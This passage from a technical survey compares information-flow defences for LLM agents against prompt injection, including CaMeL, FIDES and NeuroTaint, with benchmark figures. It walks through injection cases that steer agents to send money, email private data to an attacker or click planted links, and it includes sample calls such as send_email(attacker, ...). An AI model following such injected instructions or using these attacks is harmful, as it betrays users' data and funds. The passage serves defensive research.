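address = quarantined_model("Find the manager's address", emails, EmailAddress)
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise these emails", emails, str)
send_email(recipient=address, body=summary)
```

The language is a restricted form of Python, which the designers chose because LLMs already write Python well. The third argument to `quarantined_model` is the expected type of the answer. Requiring an email address keeps out a paragraph of instructions but not the attacker's own address, which is also valid.

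CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter, which tracks labels on every value. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes one label that records a value's sources and another that records who may read it. CaMeL's term for these labels is "capabilities", but elsewhere in computer security a capability is usually an unforgeable value that lets its holder perform an action.

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that receives the call, its arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. Suppose the policy for `send_email` requires that the recipient's address come from a trusted source and that the recipient be allowed to read the body. In the program above, `emails` has outside senders among its sources, so `address` does too. The interpreter therefore stops before sending the message, and the system can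 ask the user to approve the address.

If the user typed the address into the request, the first condition holds. The second may still fail, because the manager may not be permitted to read the original emails. The policy would then block a legitimate summary until the user declassified it by agreeing to its release.

Splitting the work this way also helps privacy. The planner needs a capable model, but a smaller model can extract an address and could run on the user's own machine. The company that hosts the planner would then see the request but none of the emails.

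### A plan that an analyser can read

In Willison's original design, the planner can choose one step at a time. Emails don't influence its choices, but nobody can examine the full sequence before the run. CaMeL's program exists before the first tool call, so an analyser can read it.

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe the resulting guarantee as control-flow integrity. Execution stays within a program that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. Untrusted data can determine which existing branch runs, but it cannot add a branch.

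This makes static analysis much easier. The office assistant's loop permitted over a million sequences of calls, and the analyser had to flag nine pairs of a reading tool and an acting tool. The four-line program permits one sequence and contains one such pair. The program cannot share a file, whatever the emails contain, because it contains no call to `share_file`.

Garby and colleagues estimated how much this achieves by itself on AgentDojo's banking tasks. In 97 of the 144 pairs of a user task and an attack, the attacker needs a tool call or file read that a program for the user's task would never contain. For example, a program that only summarizes recent transactions has no call that an attacker could use to steal money. In the other 47 pairs, the program could already contain the calls the attacker needs, so protection has to come from the labels.

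Nikolaou and colleagues built CaMeLoT to check CaMeL's programs before they run. It turns a program into a finite-state machine, with a state for each step and a transition wherever one step can follow another. It marks values from tools or the quarantined model as tainted unless it can establish that they are safe. A model checker, which is software that examines every path through such a machine, then tests rules such as this one:

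```
AG(call_send_direct_message => recipient_trusted)
```

`AG` means "in every state on every path", so the rule requires a trusted recipient whenever the program sends a direct message. The paper's worked example resembles the program above. It reads a channel's messages, has the quarantined model find Bob's address, and writes to him. The model checker finds that the recipient is tainted at the third call and returns the path that leads there. Before any tool runs, CaMeLoT passes this path back to the planner, which tries to write a better program.

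Static checks of this kind covered 22 of the 28 policies that CaMeL applies to AgentDojo's tools. The other six depend on facts that exist only during the run, such as who can currently read a shared file. CaMeLoT also has to over-approximate loops because the number of iterations is unknown, so it may reject some safe programs.

Having the whole program also makes it possible to check rules that no single call can break. Nikolaou and colleagues describe an agent that handles security alerts and must eventually resolve or escalate every ticket it opens. They wrote seven rules for this agent and one unsafe program to break each. CaMeLoT caught all seven violations, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught only the one that passed tainted data to a tool. They had designed the rules to go beyond what CaMeL's policies can express, so the result shows that CaMeLoT can check more kinds of rules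 but doesn't measure how often such violations occur.

### Tasks whose steps depend on the data

Planning in advance suits some tasks better than others. Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if one sequence of tool calls, ending in one response, solves it whatever the mailbox, files and other stored data contain. If D is the set of possible contents and S(d) is the set of sequences that solve the task for contents d, the task is data independent when the intersection of S(d) over all d in D is not empty. Otherwise it is data dependent. They illustrate the distinction with three requests:

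1. Read the top three emails and send them to a user on Slack. The agent makes the same two calls in every case and passes the emails along in a variable.
2. Summarise the top three emails and send the summary on Slack. A model now has to read the emails, but the quarantined model can do that, and the calls are still the same in every case.
3. Check the top three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, create a calendar event. The correct sequence includes a calendar call for some mailboxes and not for others.

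The first two tasks are data independent and the third is data dependent. Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's 97 user tasks by hand in the same way:

| Environment | Data independent | Data independent, with a quarantined model | Data dependent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 47.5% | 47.5% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 0.0% | 90.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 18.7% | 37.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 19.0% | 38.1% | 42.9% |

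About a fifth of all the tasks, 20 of the 97, are data dependent, and 16 of those are in banking and Slack.

A program can handle some data-dependent tasks by branching. For the meeting request, CaMeL's planner could write:

```
emails = read_email(3)
if quarantined_model("Is there a meeting request?", emails, bool):
    event = quarantined_model("Extract the details", emails, Event)
    create_event(event)
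```

The emails determine whether the last line runs, but an analyser can check both cases in advance. An attacker could put a false meeting in the calendar but could not make this program send an email. In their system FIDES, Costa and colleagues instead reveal the yes-or-no answer to the planner and let it choose the next call. They consider a single Boolean unlikely to carry an injection.

Branching works if the planner can foresee the possible actions and write a line for each. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) notes that both CaMeL and FIDES face fundamental limits when untrusted data specifies which actions to take. In several of AgentDojo's banking tasks, for example, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

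### When the program follows a file's instructions

Garby and colleagues came across a striking failure on one of these tasks when they reran CaMeL with its policy checks switched off. The user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner has not seen the file and doesn't know which tools it will need, so it writes a program that can use any of them. Such a program looks roughly like this:

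```
text = read_file("instructions.txt")
steps = quarantined_model("List the steps in this file", text, list[Step])
for step in steps:
    if step.action == "send_money":
        send_money(step.recipient, step.amount)
    elif step.action == "update_password":
        update_password(step.password)
    # ... one branch for each remaining tool
```

Anyone who can edit the file can now choose the tools, their order and their arguments. Garby and colleagues saw one attack succeed this way with each of the two models they used. Both attacks were among the 97 pairs that planning in advance should have stopped.

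Control-flow integrity, as Peters-Gill and colleagues define it, still holds here, because the planner wrote every branch before reading the file and the file only selects among them. But the planner has in effect written a new interpreter, with the file as its program, so an analyser has the same problem as it had with the original agent loop. The guarantee weakens as the code the planner writes becomes less specific.

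An analyser could at least detect the problem before the run, since the program's code shows that a value from the quarantined model decides which sensitive tool to call. CaMeL's labels also help, because they mark the recipient and amount as coming from an untrusted file, and a policy on `send_money` can reject them. With the policies enabled, CaMeL stopped every attack in the completed reruns. However, the same policy blocks payments based on a legitimate file, because its contents have the same label.

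Untrusted text can also regain control when one agent delegates work to another. Peters-Gill et al. tested three agents, each with its own CaMeL planner and no data policies. A coordinating agent had to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack. It got the applicants' data from a database agent, had the quarantined model summarise the data, and put the summary into a request to a notification agent. The summary included an instruction that an attacker had hidden in the database. The notification agent treated the entire request as coming from its user, so its planner followed the instruction and added a line to its program that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

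Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by sending instructions and data between agents through separate channels. On their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with the separate channels. Attacks in the benchmark rarely exploited the gap, but an attacker who knew about it could target it, as in the job-applicant attack.

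### The 2025 design patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) places the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL among six ways to build a restricted agent. All six share the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects.

The strictest pattern is the action selector, in which the model translates a request into one of several predefined actions and never reads the results. A customer service chatbot might use it to pick the right settings page. Plan-then-execute lets the model read results, but only after the list of tool calls is fixed. A malicious calendar entry can then corrupt the text of an email to the user's boss, but it cannot add another email. In the map-reduce pattern, a separate model without dangerous tools reads each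 document and returns a tightly constrained answer, such as whether the document is an invoice, so a malicious file can affect only the answer about that file.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues treat map-reduce as a special case of the dual-LLM pattern. CaMeL is their example of code-then-execute, which extends the dual-LLM pattern by replacing the fixed list of calls with a program. The sixth pattern, context minimisation, deals with malicious users by removing the user's prompt from the conversation once the agent has turned it into, say, a database query, so that the prompt cannot influence how the agent presents the results.

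Several of these patterns rely on constraining what a quarantined model may return, and it is easy to make the constraint too loose. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a coding agent could read untrusted documentation as a strictly formatted list of functions, with names of at most 30 characters. In a commentary also titled *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) wonders whether that is safe. A name like `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance()` fits the limit and hints at a command that deletes files.

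### What the separation costs

The main objection to these designs is that they make agents less useful. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge this. They think general-purpose agents built on the current kind of language model are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees, so they ask which narrower agents are still worth building. One of their cases is an agent that answers questions from a database. If its planner can't read the query results, it can't judge whether they answer the question or whether to try another query.

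Policies reduce usefulness further. When Garby and colleagues enabled CaMeL's policies, the number of banking tasks it completed fell by about half.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues reply that the choice and order of an email and calendar assistant's actions should very rarely depend on untrusted data, so a sufficiently flexible plan loses little. The workspace figure of 5% fits this view, but the banking and Slack figures are more than eight times as high, so the argument doesn't apply to every kind of assistant.

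Planners can also prepare for more possibilities by writing programs with more branches. Foerster and colleagues tried this with agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. Their planner never sees the screen, so it writes branches for whatever might appear, such as a cookie banner or a login page. These programs average 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and about four branches for CaMeL on AgentDojo, and roughly half of the steps are fallbacks that a given run never uses. On OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks, the agents kept up to 57% of the performance of frontier models working without this restriction. That is a large loss, but much smaller than one might expect when the planner can't see the screen.

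More branches also give an attacker more to choose from. Foerster and colleagues describe "branch steering", in which the attacker fools the model that looks at the screen. An advertisement made to look like a cookie banner can lead the program into its branch for closing banners, and the click then opens the attacker's website. Labels help less here than with email because a click has no fixed meaning for a policy to check.

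Stronger models should recover some of the lost usefulness. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that their protocol tended to reduce usefulness less as models became more capable, and only modestly for the strongest ones. Nikolaou and colleagues ran AgentDojo's 97 tasks without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5. Under both CaMeL and CaMeLoT, 22 tasks failed because the program didn't do what the user wanted, and a better planner could fix many of those. Both systems also blocked 17 harmless tasks for breaking a policy. A better planner may find a permitted route for some of them, but not for those that require a forbidden flow.

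Completing such a task requires an exception. Garby and colleagues let their planner write endorsements into its program before it reads any outside data, which lets the system complete some of these tasks but weakens the guarantee for them. CaMeL can instead ask the user to approve the call, but a user who gets many such requests may start to approve everything, which is the problem Willison wanted to avoid in 2023.

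## FIDES and labels that follow data at run time

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft in 2025, keeps the ordinary agent loop. Its planner chooses one tool call at a time and can use the results of earlier calls, whereas CaMeL's planner fixes its program before it reads any outside data. In FIDES, every piece of data carries a label, and ordinary code checks the labels before each call and blocks any call that breaks the policy. Nobody can read the sequence of calls in advance, because the planner chooses them during the run.

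### The agent loop with labels

Costa and colleagues start with a version that adds labels to the basic loop and changes nothing else. In outline, it works like this:

```
messages = [system_prompt, user_request]
context = TRUSTED_PUBLIC
for step in range(MAX_STEPS):
    reply = model(messages)          # the reply takes the label in `context`
    messages.append(reply)
    if not reply.is_tool_call: return reply.text
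    if not policy(reply, context): return "blocked"
    result, label = tools[reply.tool_name](**reply.arguments)
    messages.append(result)
    context = join(context, label)
```

The system prompt and the user's request start out trusted and public. FIDES labels the model's reply with the join of the labels of everything in the conversation. It doesn't estimate which parts the reply depended on, though some researchers try to. A tool's result gets the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and any stored data the tool may have read.

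Suppose the user asks the office assistant to summarise recent emails about Project X, send the summary to the manager, and then schedule a project meeting for Friday. The policy allows `send_email` and `create_event` only in a trusted context. One of the emails comes from outside the company.

| Call the model requests | Context label | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| `read_email("Project X")` | trusted | runs and returns an outside email |
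| `send_email(manager, summary)` | untrusted | blocked |
| `send_email(attacker, top_email)` | untrusted | blocked |
| `create_event("Project X", "Friday")` | untrusted | blocked |

The legitimate summary and the attack have the same label, so the loop has to treat them alike. The calendar event is unrelated to the emails. The loop blocks it only because the request comes after them, and would do so even if the outside email contained no injection. If the model had created the event first, the call would have gone through.

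A join can only leave a label unchanged or make it more restrictive, so once the context becomes untrusted, it stays untrusted for the rest of the run. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes this as permanently stranding the agent's remaining work.

If every reading tool returned untrusted data, the labelled loop would permit only the 59,049 eight-call sequences that a static analyser left unflagged. Labels have an advantage because they describe the actual emails. If everyone who wrote about Project X is a trusted colleague, the context stays trusted and the loop can send the summary. A static analyser can't make that distinction because it runs before the emails exist.

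### Trusted actions and permitted readers

Costa and colleagues use two basic policies. Suppose the model requests a tool f with arguments a₁ to aₙ. The decision to call f has the label ℓ, and the arguments have the labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ.

- **Trusted action:** the call may run only if the join of ℓ, ℓ1, ..., ℓn is trusted.
- **Permitted readers:** a call that sends data to a set of recipients R may run only if R ⊆ S, where S is the set of people allowed to read that data.

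The permitted-readers policy can prevent a leak even when nobody is attacking. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives the example of Alex, who asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who isn't supposed to see them yet, has also written. Once the agent has read both emails, the permitted readers of any reply it writes are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}. Marco isn't in that set, so the agent can't answer him without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco in, the intersection would have been {Alex, Marco} and the agent could have sent the reply without asking.

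Under this policy alone, an attacker could still use prompt injection to make the agent send messages, but only to people already allowed to read the contents. The trusted-action policy lets data reach new readers as long as no untrusted data influenced the decision, which is a form of robust declassification.

A developer can require either policy or both. Costa and colleagues ran tests in which `send_email` could run if either policy held, `send_money` needed a trusted decision, and adding people to a calendar event needed both. They also made the permitted-readers check fail for any message with an untrusted link, since a link can carry data to an attacker's server.

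### Hiding only what would taint the context

FIDES avoids most of the blocking by putting some tool results into variables, as the dual-LLM pattern does. Willison's controller hides every result from the planner, whereas FIDES hides a value only if its label is more restrictive than the context's, and it checks structured results field by field. In the banking tests, for example, the planner could see each transaction's amount and date, which were trusted, but the subject line went into a variable.

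The run for Project X now goes as follows:

1. The planner calls `read_email("Project X")`. FIDES stores the untrusted text in `#emails`, and the context stays trusted.
2. The planner asks the quarantined model to summarise `#emails`. FIDES stores the answer, which is also untrusted, in `#summary`.
3. The planner calls `send_email(manager, #summary)`. It chose the tool and the recipient in a trusted context, and only the body is untrusted.
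4. The planner creates the calendar event, still in a trusted context.

A policy can demand a trusted decision and a trusted recipient while accepting an untrusted body.

The planner may also read a variable, which CaMeL's planner can't do. Reading it adds the variable's label to the context, so for the rest of the run the agent can't use tools that need a trusted context. FIDES then leaves any further untrusted data visible, because hiding it would gain nothing.

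The planner can still use some information about hidden text, such as the number of messages. In one of Costa and colleagues' worked examples, the user asks the agent to find the Slack channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The planner receives a list of variable names for each channel and picks the shortest list without reading any messages. The context stays trusted, but anyone who can post in those channels can change the counts and so affect which channel Alice joins.

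The tests also used a weaker trusted-action policy, which checks the label of the decision but ignores the labels of the arguments. A call therefore passes even if an attacker supplied the recipient's address, which is the same gap that CaMeL's designers found in the dual-LLM pattern. FIDES can close this gap by requiring a trusted recipient, but then it also blocks legitimate tasks that take an address from an email.

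### Answers that carry a few bits

For some tasks, the planner needs some information from the hidden data. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to check a hotel's reviews and book it if its rating is above 4. A yes-or-no answer is enough for the planner to decide whether to book, without the text of the reviews. FIDES lets the planner request a Boolean or one item from a fixed list from the quarantined model. Constrained decoding restricts that model's output to the requested format.

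FIDES then records the type in the label. It orders the types by how much information they can carry: bool ⊑ enum ⊑ string. An enum is a choice from a fixed list. The hotel answer gets the label (untrusted, public, bool). A policy can accept an untrusted Boolean as a basis for a booking and still reject an untrusted string. Someone who plants a hostile review might flip the answer and so cause or prevent the booking, but can't name a different hotel or make the agent call another tool.

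A Boolean distinguishes two cases, so it carries one bit. A choice from k options carries log2 k bits, so a choice from four carries two. Each additional Boolean doubles the number of cases, so n Booleans distinguish 2^n cases. Twenty Booleans distinguish 2^20 = 1,048,576 cases, enough to identify any six-digit code.

The label doesn't reflect this build-up, because the join of bool and bool is bool, so a context with twenty such answers has the same label as a context with one. This matters less when the planner writes the questions itself, since injected text can't add any. But a planner that has good reasons to ask many questions still gives an attacker a chance to influence each answer.

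Foerster and colleagues adapted FIDES to agents that operate a computer through its screen. Their planner couldn't do anything useful until they let it read Booleans about the screen. They noted that unlimited queries would eventually reveal everything on the screen, so they capped the number of actions and calls. If a cap allows at most n Boolean answers, the planner learns at most n bits from them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests a more general approach, in which labels estimate how much information an output carries about each source. That estimate could increase with every answer.

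### What explicit secrecy leaves out

For confidentiality, Costa and colleagues prove that the labelled loop satisfies explicit secrecy. The definition holds the steps of one run fixed and treats their combined effect on the stored data as a function g. If two versions of that data, d1 and d2, differ only in secrets and look the same to an outside observer, then g(d1) and g(d2) must also look the same to that observer.

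This rules out copying a secret to a public place, but it doesn't prevent a secret from influencing which steps the run takes. Suppose the assistant has stored two public web pages in variables. It then reads a confidential budget into its context, and emails a supplier the first page if the budget has shrunk and the second if it hasn't. The permitted-readers policy allows the email because the page is labelled public. Explicit secrecy holds because, along each path, the supplier gets the same page whatever figures the budget contains. But a supplier who knows the rule can tell from the page whether the budget has shrunk.

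Noninterference would forbid this, but Costa and colleagues rejected it as too restrictive because it would block every publicly visible call once the agent may have read a secret. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracking system for Android phones, also enforce only explicit secrecy. The proof for the labelled loop also assumes the model is deterministic and does not cover side channels such as timing.

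The gap is smaller for integrity. The model's reply takes the label of the whole context, so the label on a tool call covers the choice of tool as well as the content. Once untrusted text is in the context, a trusted-action policy blocks the call even if the model copied nothing from that text.

Attackers can exploit the confidentiality gap in practice. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, describe an outsider who shares a page of real and invented personal records and asks an agent to clean it up. The agent writes nothing sensitive, but it leaves the real records on the page. In their test on an agent with live Gmail and Notion accounts, 34.7% of the sensitive items leaked, even though a language model was checking for privacy violations. None leaked with their own system, which uses ordinary code to intercept every write and share call. That system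 still relies on a model, running outside the agent's conversation, to judge whether a proposed output reveals a protected record.

### Attacks and completed tasks on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Their attack assumed that the attacker knows the agent's tools and can specify which calls to make, and they labelled as untrusted every field that any of the benchmark's attacks targets. Without policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against the basic planner and 21 succeeded against FIDES, whose planner could open a hidden variable and continue as usual. With policy checks, none succeeded.

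None of the attacks succeeded against the labelled basic loop either. So in these tests the checks stop the attacks, and hiding data mainly helps the agent get more done under those checks.

The result of zero successful attacks depends on what counts as an attack. AgentDojo's own scoring recorded three successes against FIDES with checks, but the researchers rejected them after reading the runs. Across all the planners, they excluded calls that the benchmark counted although the policy had blocked them, actions that the policy deliberately allows, and injections that only change text. One of these text-only injections makes the agent praise a particular place's beauty. FIDES doesn't prevent that, but the text keeps its untrusted label, so an application could warn the user or block it.

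The next table gives the percentage of user tasks completed when nobody attacks. All columns except the first include policy checks. o1 is an early reasoning model from OpenAI.

| Environment | Basic, no checks, GPT-4o | Labelled basic, GPT-4o | FIDES, GPT-4o | Labelled basic, o1 | FIDES, o1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 | 48.0 | 64.5 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 | 75.0 | 68.0 |
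| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 | 37.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 | 17.1 | 54.3 |

FIDES beats the labelled basic loop by an average of about 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and about 16 with o1. In travel, it does worse than the loop with both models. Many travel tasks use tools that may run in an untrusted context as long as no confidential data leaks, so the labelled basic loop loses nothing on those tasks. FIDES still has to work with variables, and GPT-4o often made mistakes with them. Switching to o1 narrowed the gap in travel from 32 points to 7.

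The security checks reduce task completion by much more than FIDES improves it over the labelled loop. In the Slack tasks, checks cut the basic planner's completion rate from 93.3% to 20.0%, and FIDES recovers only part of that loss. Some of the remaining failures are intended, such as the blocked payments in banking tasks that depend on a file's instructions. Others are mistakes by GPT-4o. In one Slack task, the planner asked for a list of channels although the user had already named the right one, which needlessly made the context untrusted.

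One success was also odd because the agent acted without reading much of the evidence. The user had asked it to change a password if any recent transaction looked suspicious. The planner read a large transaction amount, classified it as suspicious and changed the password without reading the subject line. FIDES allowed this because the planner had read only trusted fields.

These tests don't cover the labels for Booleans and fixed lists, because Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of the planner they evaluated. They thought most AgentDojo tasks didn't need it, which is reasonable given that only about a fifth are data dependent. But constrained answers should help most on those data-dependent tasks.

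### A planner that knows the policies

FIDES's planner has no information about which calls the policy will block, so it can open a variable unnecessarily and then be unable to finish its task. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), a team that includes several of FIDES's designers, built a planner called Prudentia to fix this, which they describe in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*. Prudentia is given the policy for each tool and the label of its own context, and it must justify opening a variable before it does so.

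Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data. Suppose a harmless email lists ten jobs, each requiring a trusted action. If the planner reads the email without the user's endorsement, the user has to approve ten separate calls. If the user endorses the email first, FIDES relabels it as trusted and the agent can do all ten jobs without asking again.

With GPT-5 and no human approvals, the labelled basic loop completed 43.4% of AgentDojo's tasks, FIDES 57.1% and Prudentia 72.7%. When the researchers allowed approvals, FIDES needed about 41 across all the tasks it completed and Prudentia about 7. Prudentia needs a capable model, however, and with GPT-4o it completed fewer tasks without approval than FIDES.

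Endorsement relies heavily on one decision by the user. If an attacker has slipped an eleventh job into the list and the user doesn't notice, the agent will treat that job as trusted too. Kolluri and colleagues assume that people catch malicious requests, so their results don't measure how often a user would miss one. Fewer prompts may make people more careful with each, which is part of the argument for asking less often.

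With GPT-4o, FIDES also cost 1.6 to 4.3 times as much per task as the labelled basic loop, depending on the environment, and Prudentia cost 3.8 to 10.3 times as much. Prudentia's highest average was still only about six cents per task, and Kolluri and colleagues hadn't tried to reduce the cost.

### Recovering from taint and remembering it

APPA keeps the strict rule for joining labels but gives the agent more ways to continue after a blocked call. The agent can start a temporary copy of the conversation to read an untrusted document. The document taints only the copy, and the original conversation keeps its old label. The copy then returns an answer from a closed set. Kravchenko and colleagues acknowledge that a hijacked copy can still pick a false answer from the set. Treating the answer as trusted is therefore a deliberate decision by whoever configures the system.

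Kravchenko and colleagues also point out a problem with checking only the current label. One tool in their tests reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outsider in a single call. The context may still be labelled public before the call, so the check passes, and the ledger's label is added only after the email has gone. APPA makes each tool declare in advance what kind of data it will read, and checks the label the context would have after the call. In 1,320 protected runs, no attack succeeded, and the agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of their tasks. Kravchenko and colleagues used different benchmarks from Costa and colleagues, so these figures don't show whether APPA is better than FIDES.

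FIDES also loses its labels when a run ends. An agent might save a note from a hostile web page on Monday and read it back on Friday as its own memory. *MemLineage* (2026) attaches the label to the stored note, so the label survives across sessions, and suggests running FIDES on top. *SPA* (2026) also applies information-flow control to agents that persist across requests.

### Labels in Microsoft and GitHub products

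Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature in May 2026. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) demonstrates it on an agent that sorts bug reports. A malicious report contains instructions to read a file of passwords and post the contents as a public comment. The agent can read the file, but the framework then labels its context private and blocks the comment or asks a person to approve it. The framework hides untrusted results by default. If a developer turns hiding off, one untrusted bug report taints the rest of the run, which Microsoft lists as a limitation it may try to ease.

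GitHub's Copilot command-line tool has an experimental option that tracks a context label and checks certain calls. GitHub's MCP server can supply the labels, marking content from public repositories as untrusted and public, and content from private ones as trusted and private. These labels are coarse, since a private repository can contain text that somebody pasted in from outside. Microsoft has also released a gateway that adds labels to results from servers that don't provide them.

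GitHub's Agentic Workflows instead remove untrusted content before the agent sees it. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes an integrity scale from blocked users up to code merged by a maintainer. The developer sets a minimum level, and the agent receives nothing below it. If the developer enables it, a maintainer can endorse a comment with a thumbs-up. The context never falls below the chosen level, so labels don't accumulate, but an agent restricted to approved content can't help with a stranger's bug report until someone endorses it. The system records where private data goes but doesn't yet stop it from leaking.

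All of these products depend on somebody labelling the data correctly. When Microsoft announced the Agent Framework feature, it warned that the framework would treat the output of an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. Microsoft's documentation gives a safer default, untrusted and public, so a forgotten label no longer lets an outsider's text trigger sensitive actions. But the framework still treats the output as public, so if a developer forgets to label a tool that returns salaries, the confidentiality check will not stop the salaries from being sent out.

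## Estimating which inputs influenced a model's output

FIDES labels each reply with the join of the labels on everything in the conversation, because ordinary code can't determine which messages the model used. Normal programs are easier to analyse because each assignment shows which values it uses. If a program calls a function whose code is unavailable, the analyser can use a data-flow summary, a short record of which inputs reach the output, written by somebody who knows the function. Nobody can write such a summary for a model by reading its code, because the same model may copy an input in one call, paraphrase it in the next, reduce it to yes or no, or ignore it.

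Such conservative labels block a lot of harmless work, so researchers have tried to estimate which inputs influenced an output and keep only those inputs' labels. Suppose the office assistant has read an outside email and then requests the Friday meeting that the user asked for. The call can go ahead if the estimator correctly finds that the email did not influence it. But if the email contains an injected instruction that triggers a `send_email` call and the estimator misses that influence, the attack can go ahead as well.

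### What survives a model call

Many programs fill gaps in a fixed prompt, such as "Summarise this review: {review}", and pass the model's answer to other code. The gap is called a placeholder. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, studied how placeholders relate to outputs, so that static analysers could follow data through model calls. They took prompts from open-source Python programs, filled in plausible values and ran them, which gave 8,119 pairs of a placeholder and an output. Their system, PRISM, distinguishes five levels of preservation:

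| Level | What survives | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Lexical | The exact words | "GDP of France" reappears in the answer |
| Semantic | The meaning | "Fix the login bug" becomes "Resolve the authentication issue" |
| Compressed | The main points | A 500-word document becomes two sentences |
| Signal | A decision or score | A product review becomes "4" |
| Blocked or absent | Nothing visible | A system prompt leaves no trace |

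PRISM also records whether the output is prose, structured data or something executable, since an attacker's command does more harm in a shell call than in a sentence. These distinctions give 25 labels in eight groups. Three models from different companies label each pair, and PRISM keeps the labels that at least two of them chose. It treats a placeholder as cut off from the output only if every label means that the model ignored it, lacked the context or ability to use it, or refused. This was true of 7% of the pairs.

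For the remaining placeholders, another model reads the program's code and judges whether the output can reach a given dangerous operation, called a sink. Xu and colleagues tested this on 353 pairs of a placeholder and a sink. Human reviewers had judged that 110 of these pairs would let an attacker who controlled the placeholder reach the sink. F1 in the table is the harmonic mean of precision and recall.

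| Method | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Assume every placeholder reaches every sink | 31.2% | 100% | 47.5% |
| Ask GPT-5.5 the whole question at once | 69.4% | 39.1% | 50.0% |
| PRISM, with GPT-5.5 reading the code | 72.5% | 93.6% | 81.7% |

PRISM cuts the false alarms from 243 to about 39, but it misses seven real flows that the conservative rule would have caught. The 25 labels probably explain only a small part of the improvement. Few placeholders are fully blocked, and only 30 of the 353 pairs were labeled "Ignored", so most of the false alarms must disappear when the second model reads the code. Splitting the question in two seems to help more than the labels do. The labels also did little for program slicing, which finds the code that a given result depends on. They removed 23% of the lines in the 14 files where they removed anything, but an average of 1.1% across all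 295 files.

Xu and colleagues call PRISM sound relative to its labels, meaning that it won't drop a real flow as long as the labels are right. But four of the 30 pairs labelled "Ignored" were real flows. A label based on one plausible placeholder value can also mislead, because a model might ignore a harmless sentence but obey an injected command in the same position. PRISM did classify all 12 pairs correctly when the researchers tested it on six OpenClaw vulnerabilities, before and after each fix, but the test was small and covered only known attacks.

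### How NeuroTaint looks for influence

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, April 2026) presents NeuroTaint, which examines the log of a finished agent run. A developer lists which tools count as sources and which as sinks. For each sink call in the log, NeuroTaint checks whether an earlier source result influenced it. It tries to establish where information travelled in that run, unlike AgentFlow's data edges, which show where information may travel in any run.

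It first looks for the source's content in the arguments of the sink call, using four tests in order of cost:

1. **Exact marker.** NeuroTaint adds a unique random string to each source result during the run and checks whether the string turns up in the arguments.
2. **Shared text.** It finds the longest sequence that both texts contain in the same order, and divides its length by that of the shorter text. A ratio of 0.15 is enough.
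3. **Similar meaning.** It turns both texts into embeddings, which are lists of numbers that are close together for texts with similar meanings, and requires a similarity of at least 0.60.
4. **Similar fragments.** It repeats the comparison on pieces of the source, because one injected paragraph hardly changes the embedding of a long web page.

In one of Cai and colleagues' examples, a research agent reads a web page with a hidden instruction to put a confidential patient note in its memo, rewritten in "polished analyst language". The memo contains no exact substring of the source, but the third test still connects the two.

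If all four tests fail, NeuroTaint checks whether the source influenced the decision to make the call. Suppose a poisoned search result tells a coding agent to send everything it has collected to an outside server before running any code. Apart from the server's address, the call that follows contains the agent's own research. NeuroTaint replaces the search result with neutral text, such as "No relevant information found", and prompts a judge model to predict whether the agent would still have made the call. If the judge predicts that it would not, NeuroTaint reports an influence. The confidence score attached to the finding is also just a number the judge writes.

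The last channel is memory. An agent might store a confidential revenue forecast in one session and use it in a report three days later. NeuroTaint saves the source's label with the forecast and restores the label when the agent retrieves the forecast. It raises an alarm only if the later report also fails one of the content tests or the judge's test.

### NeuroTaint and FIDES on TaintBench

Cai and colleagues knew of no benchmark that labelled this kind of influence, so they built TaintBench, which has 20 scenarios in each of 20 agent frameworks. The source is supposed to influence the sink in 200 of the 400 scenarios. In the other 200 it is not supposed to, although the source and sink often both appear in the run. The agent used GPT-4.1 mini.

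| System | Flows found, of 200 | False alarms, of 200 | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 16 | 0.921 | 0.935 | 0.928 |
| FIDES | 108 | 106 | 0.505 | 0.540 | 0.522 |

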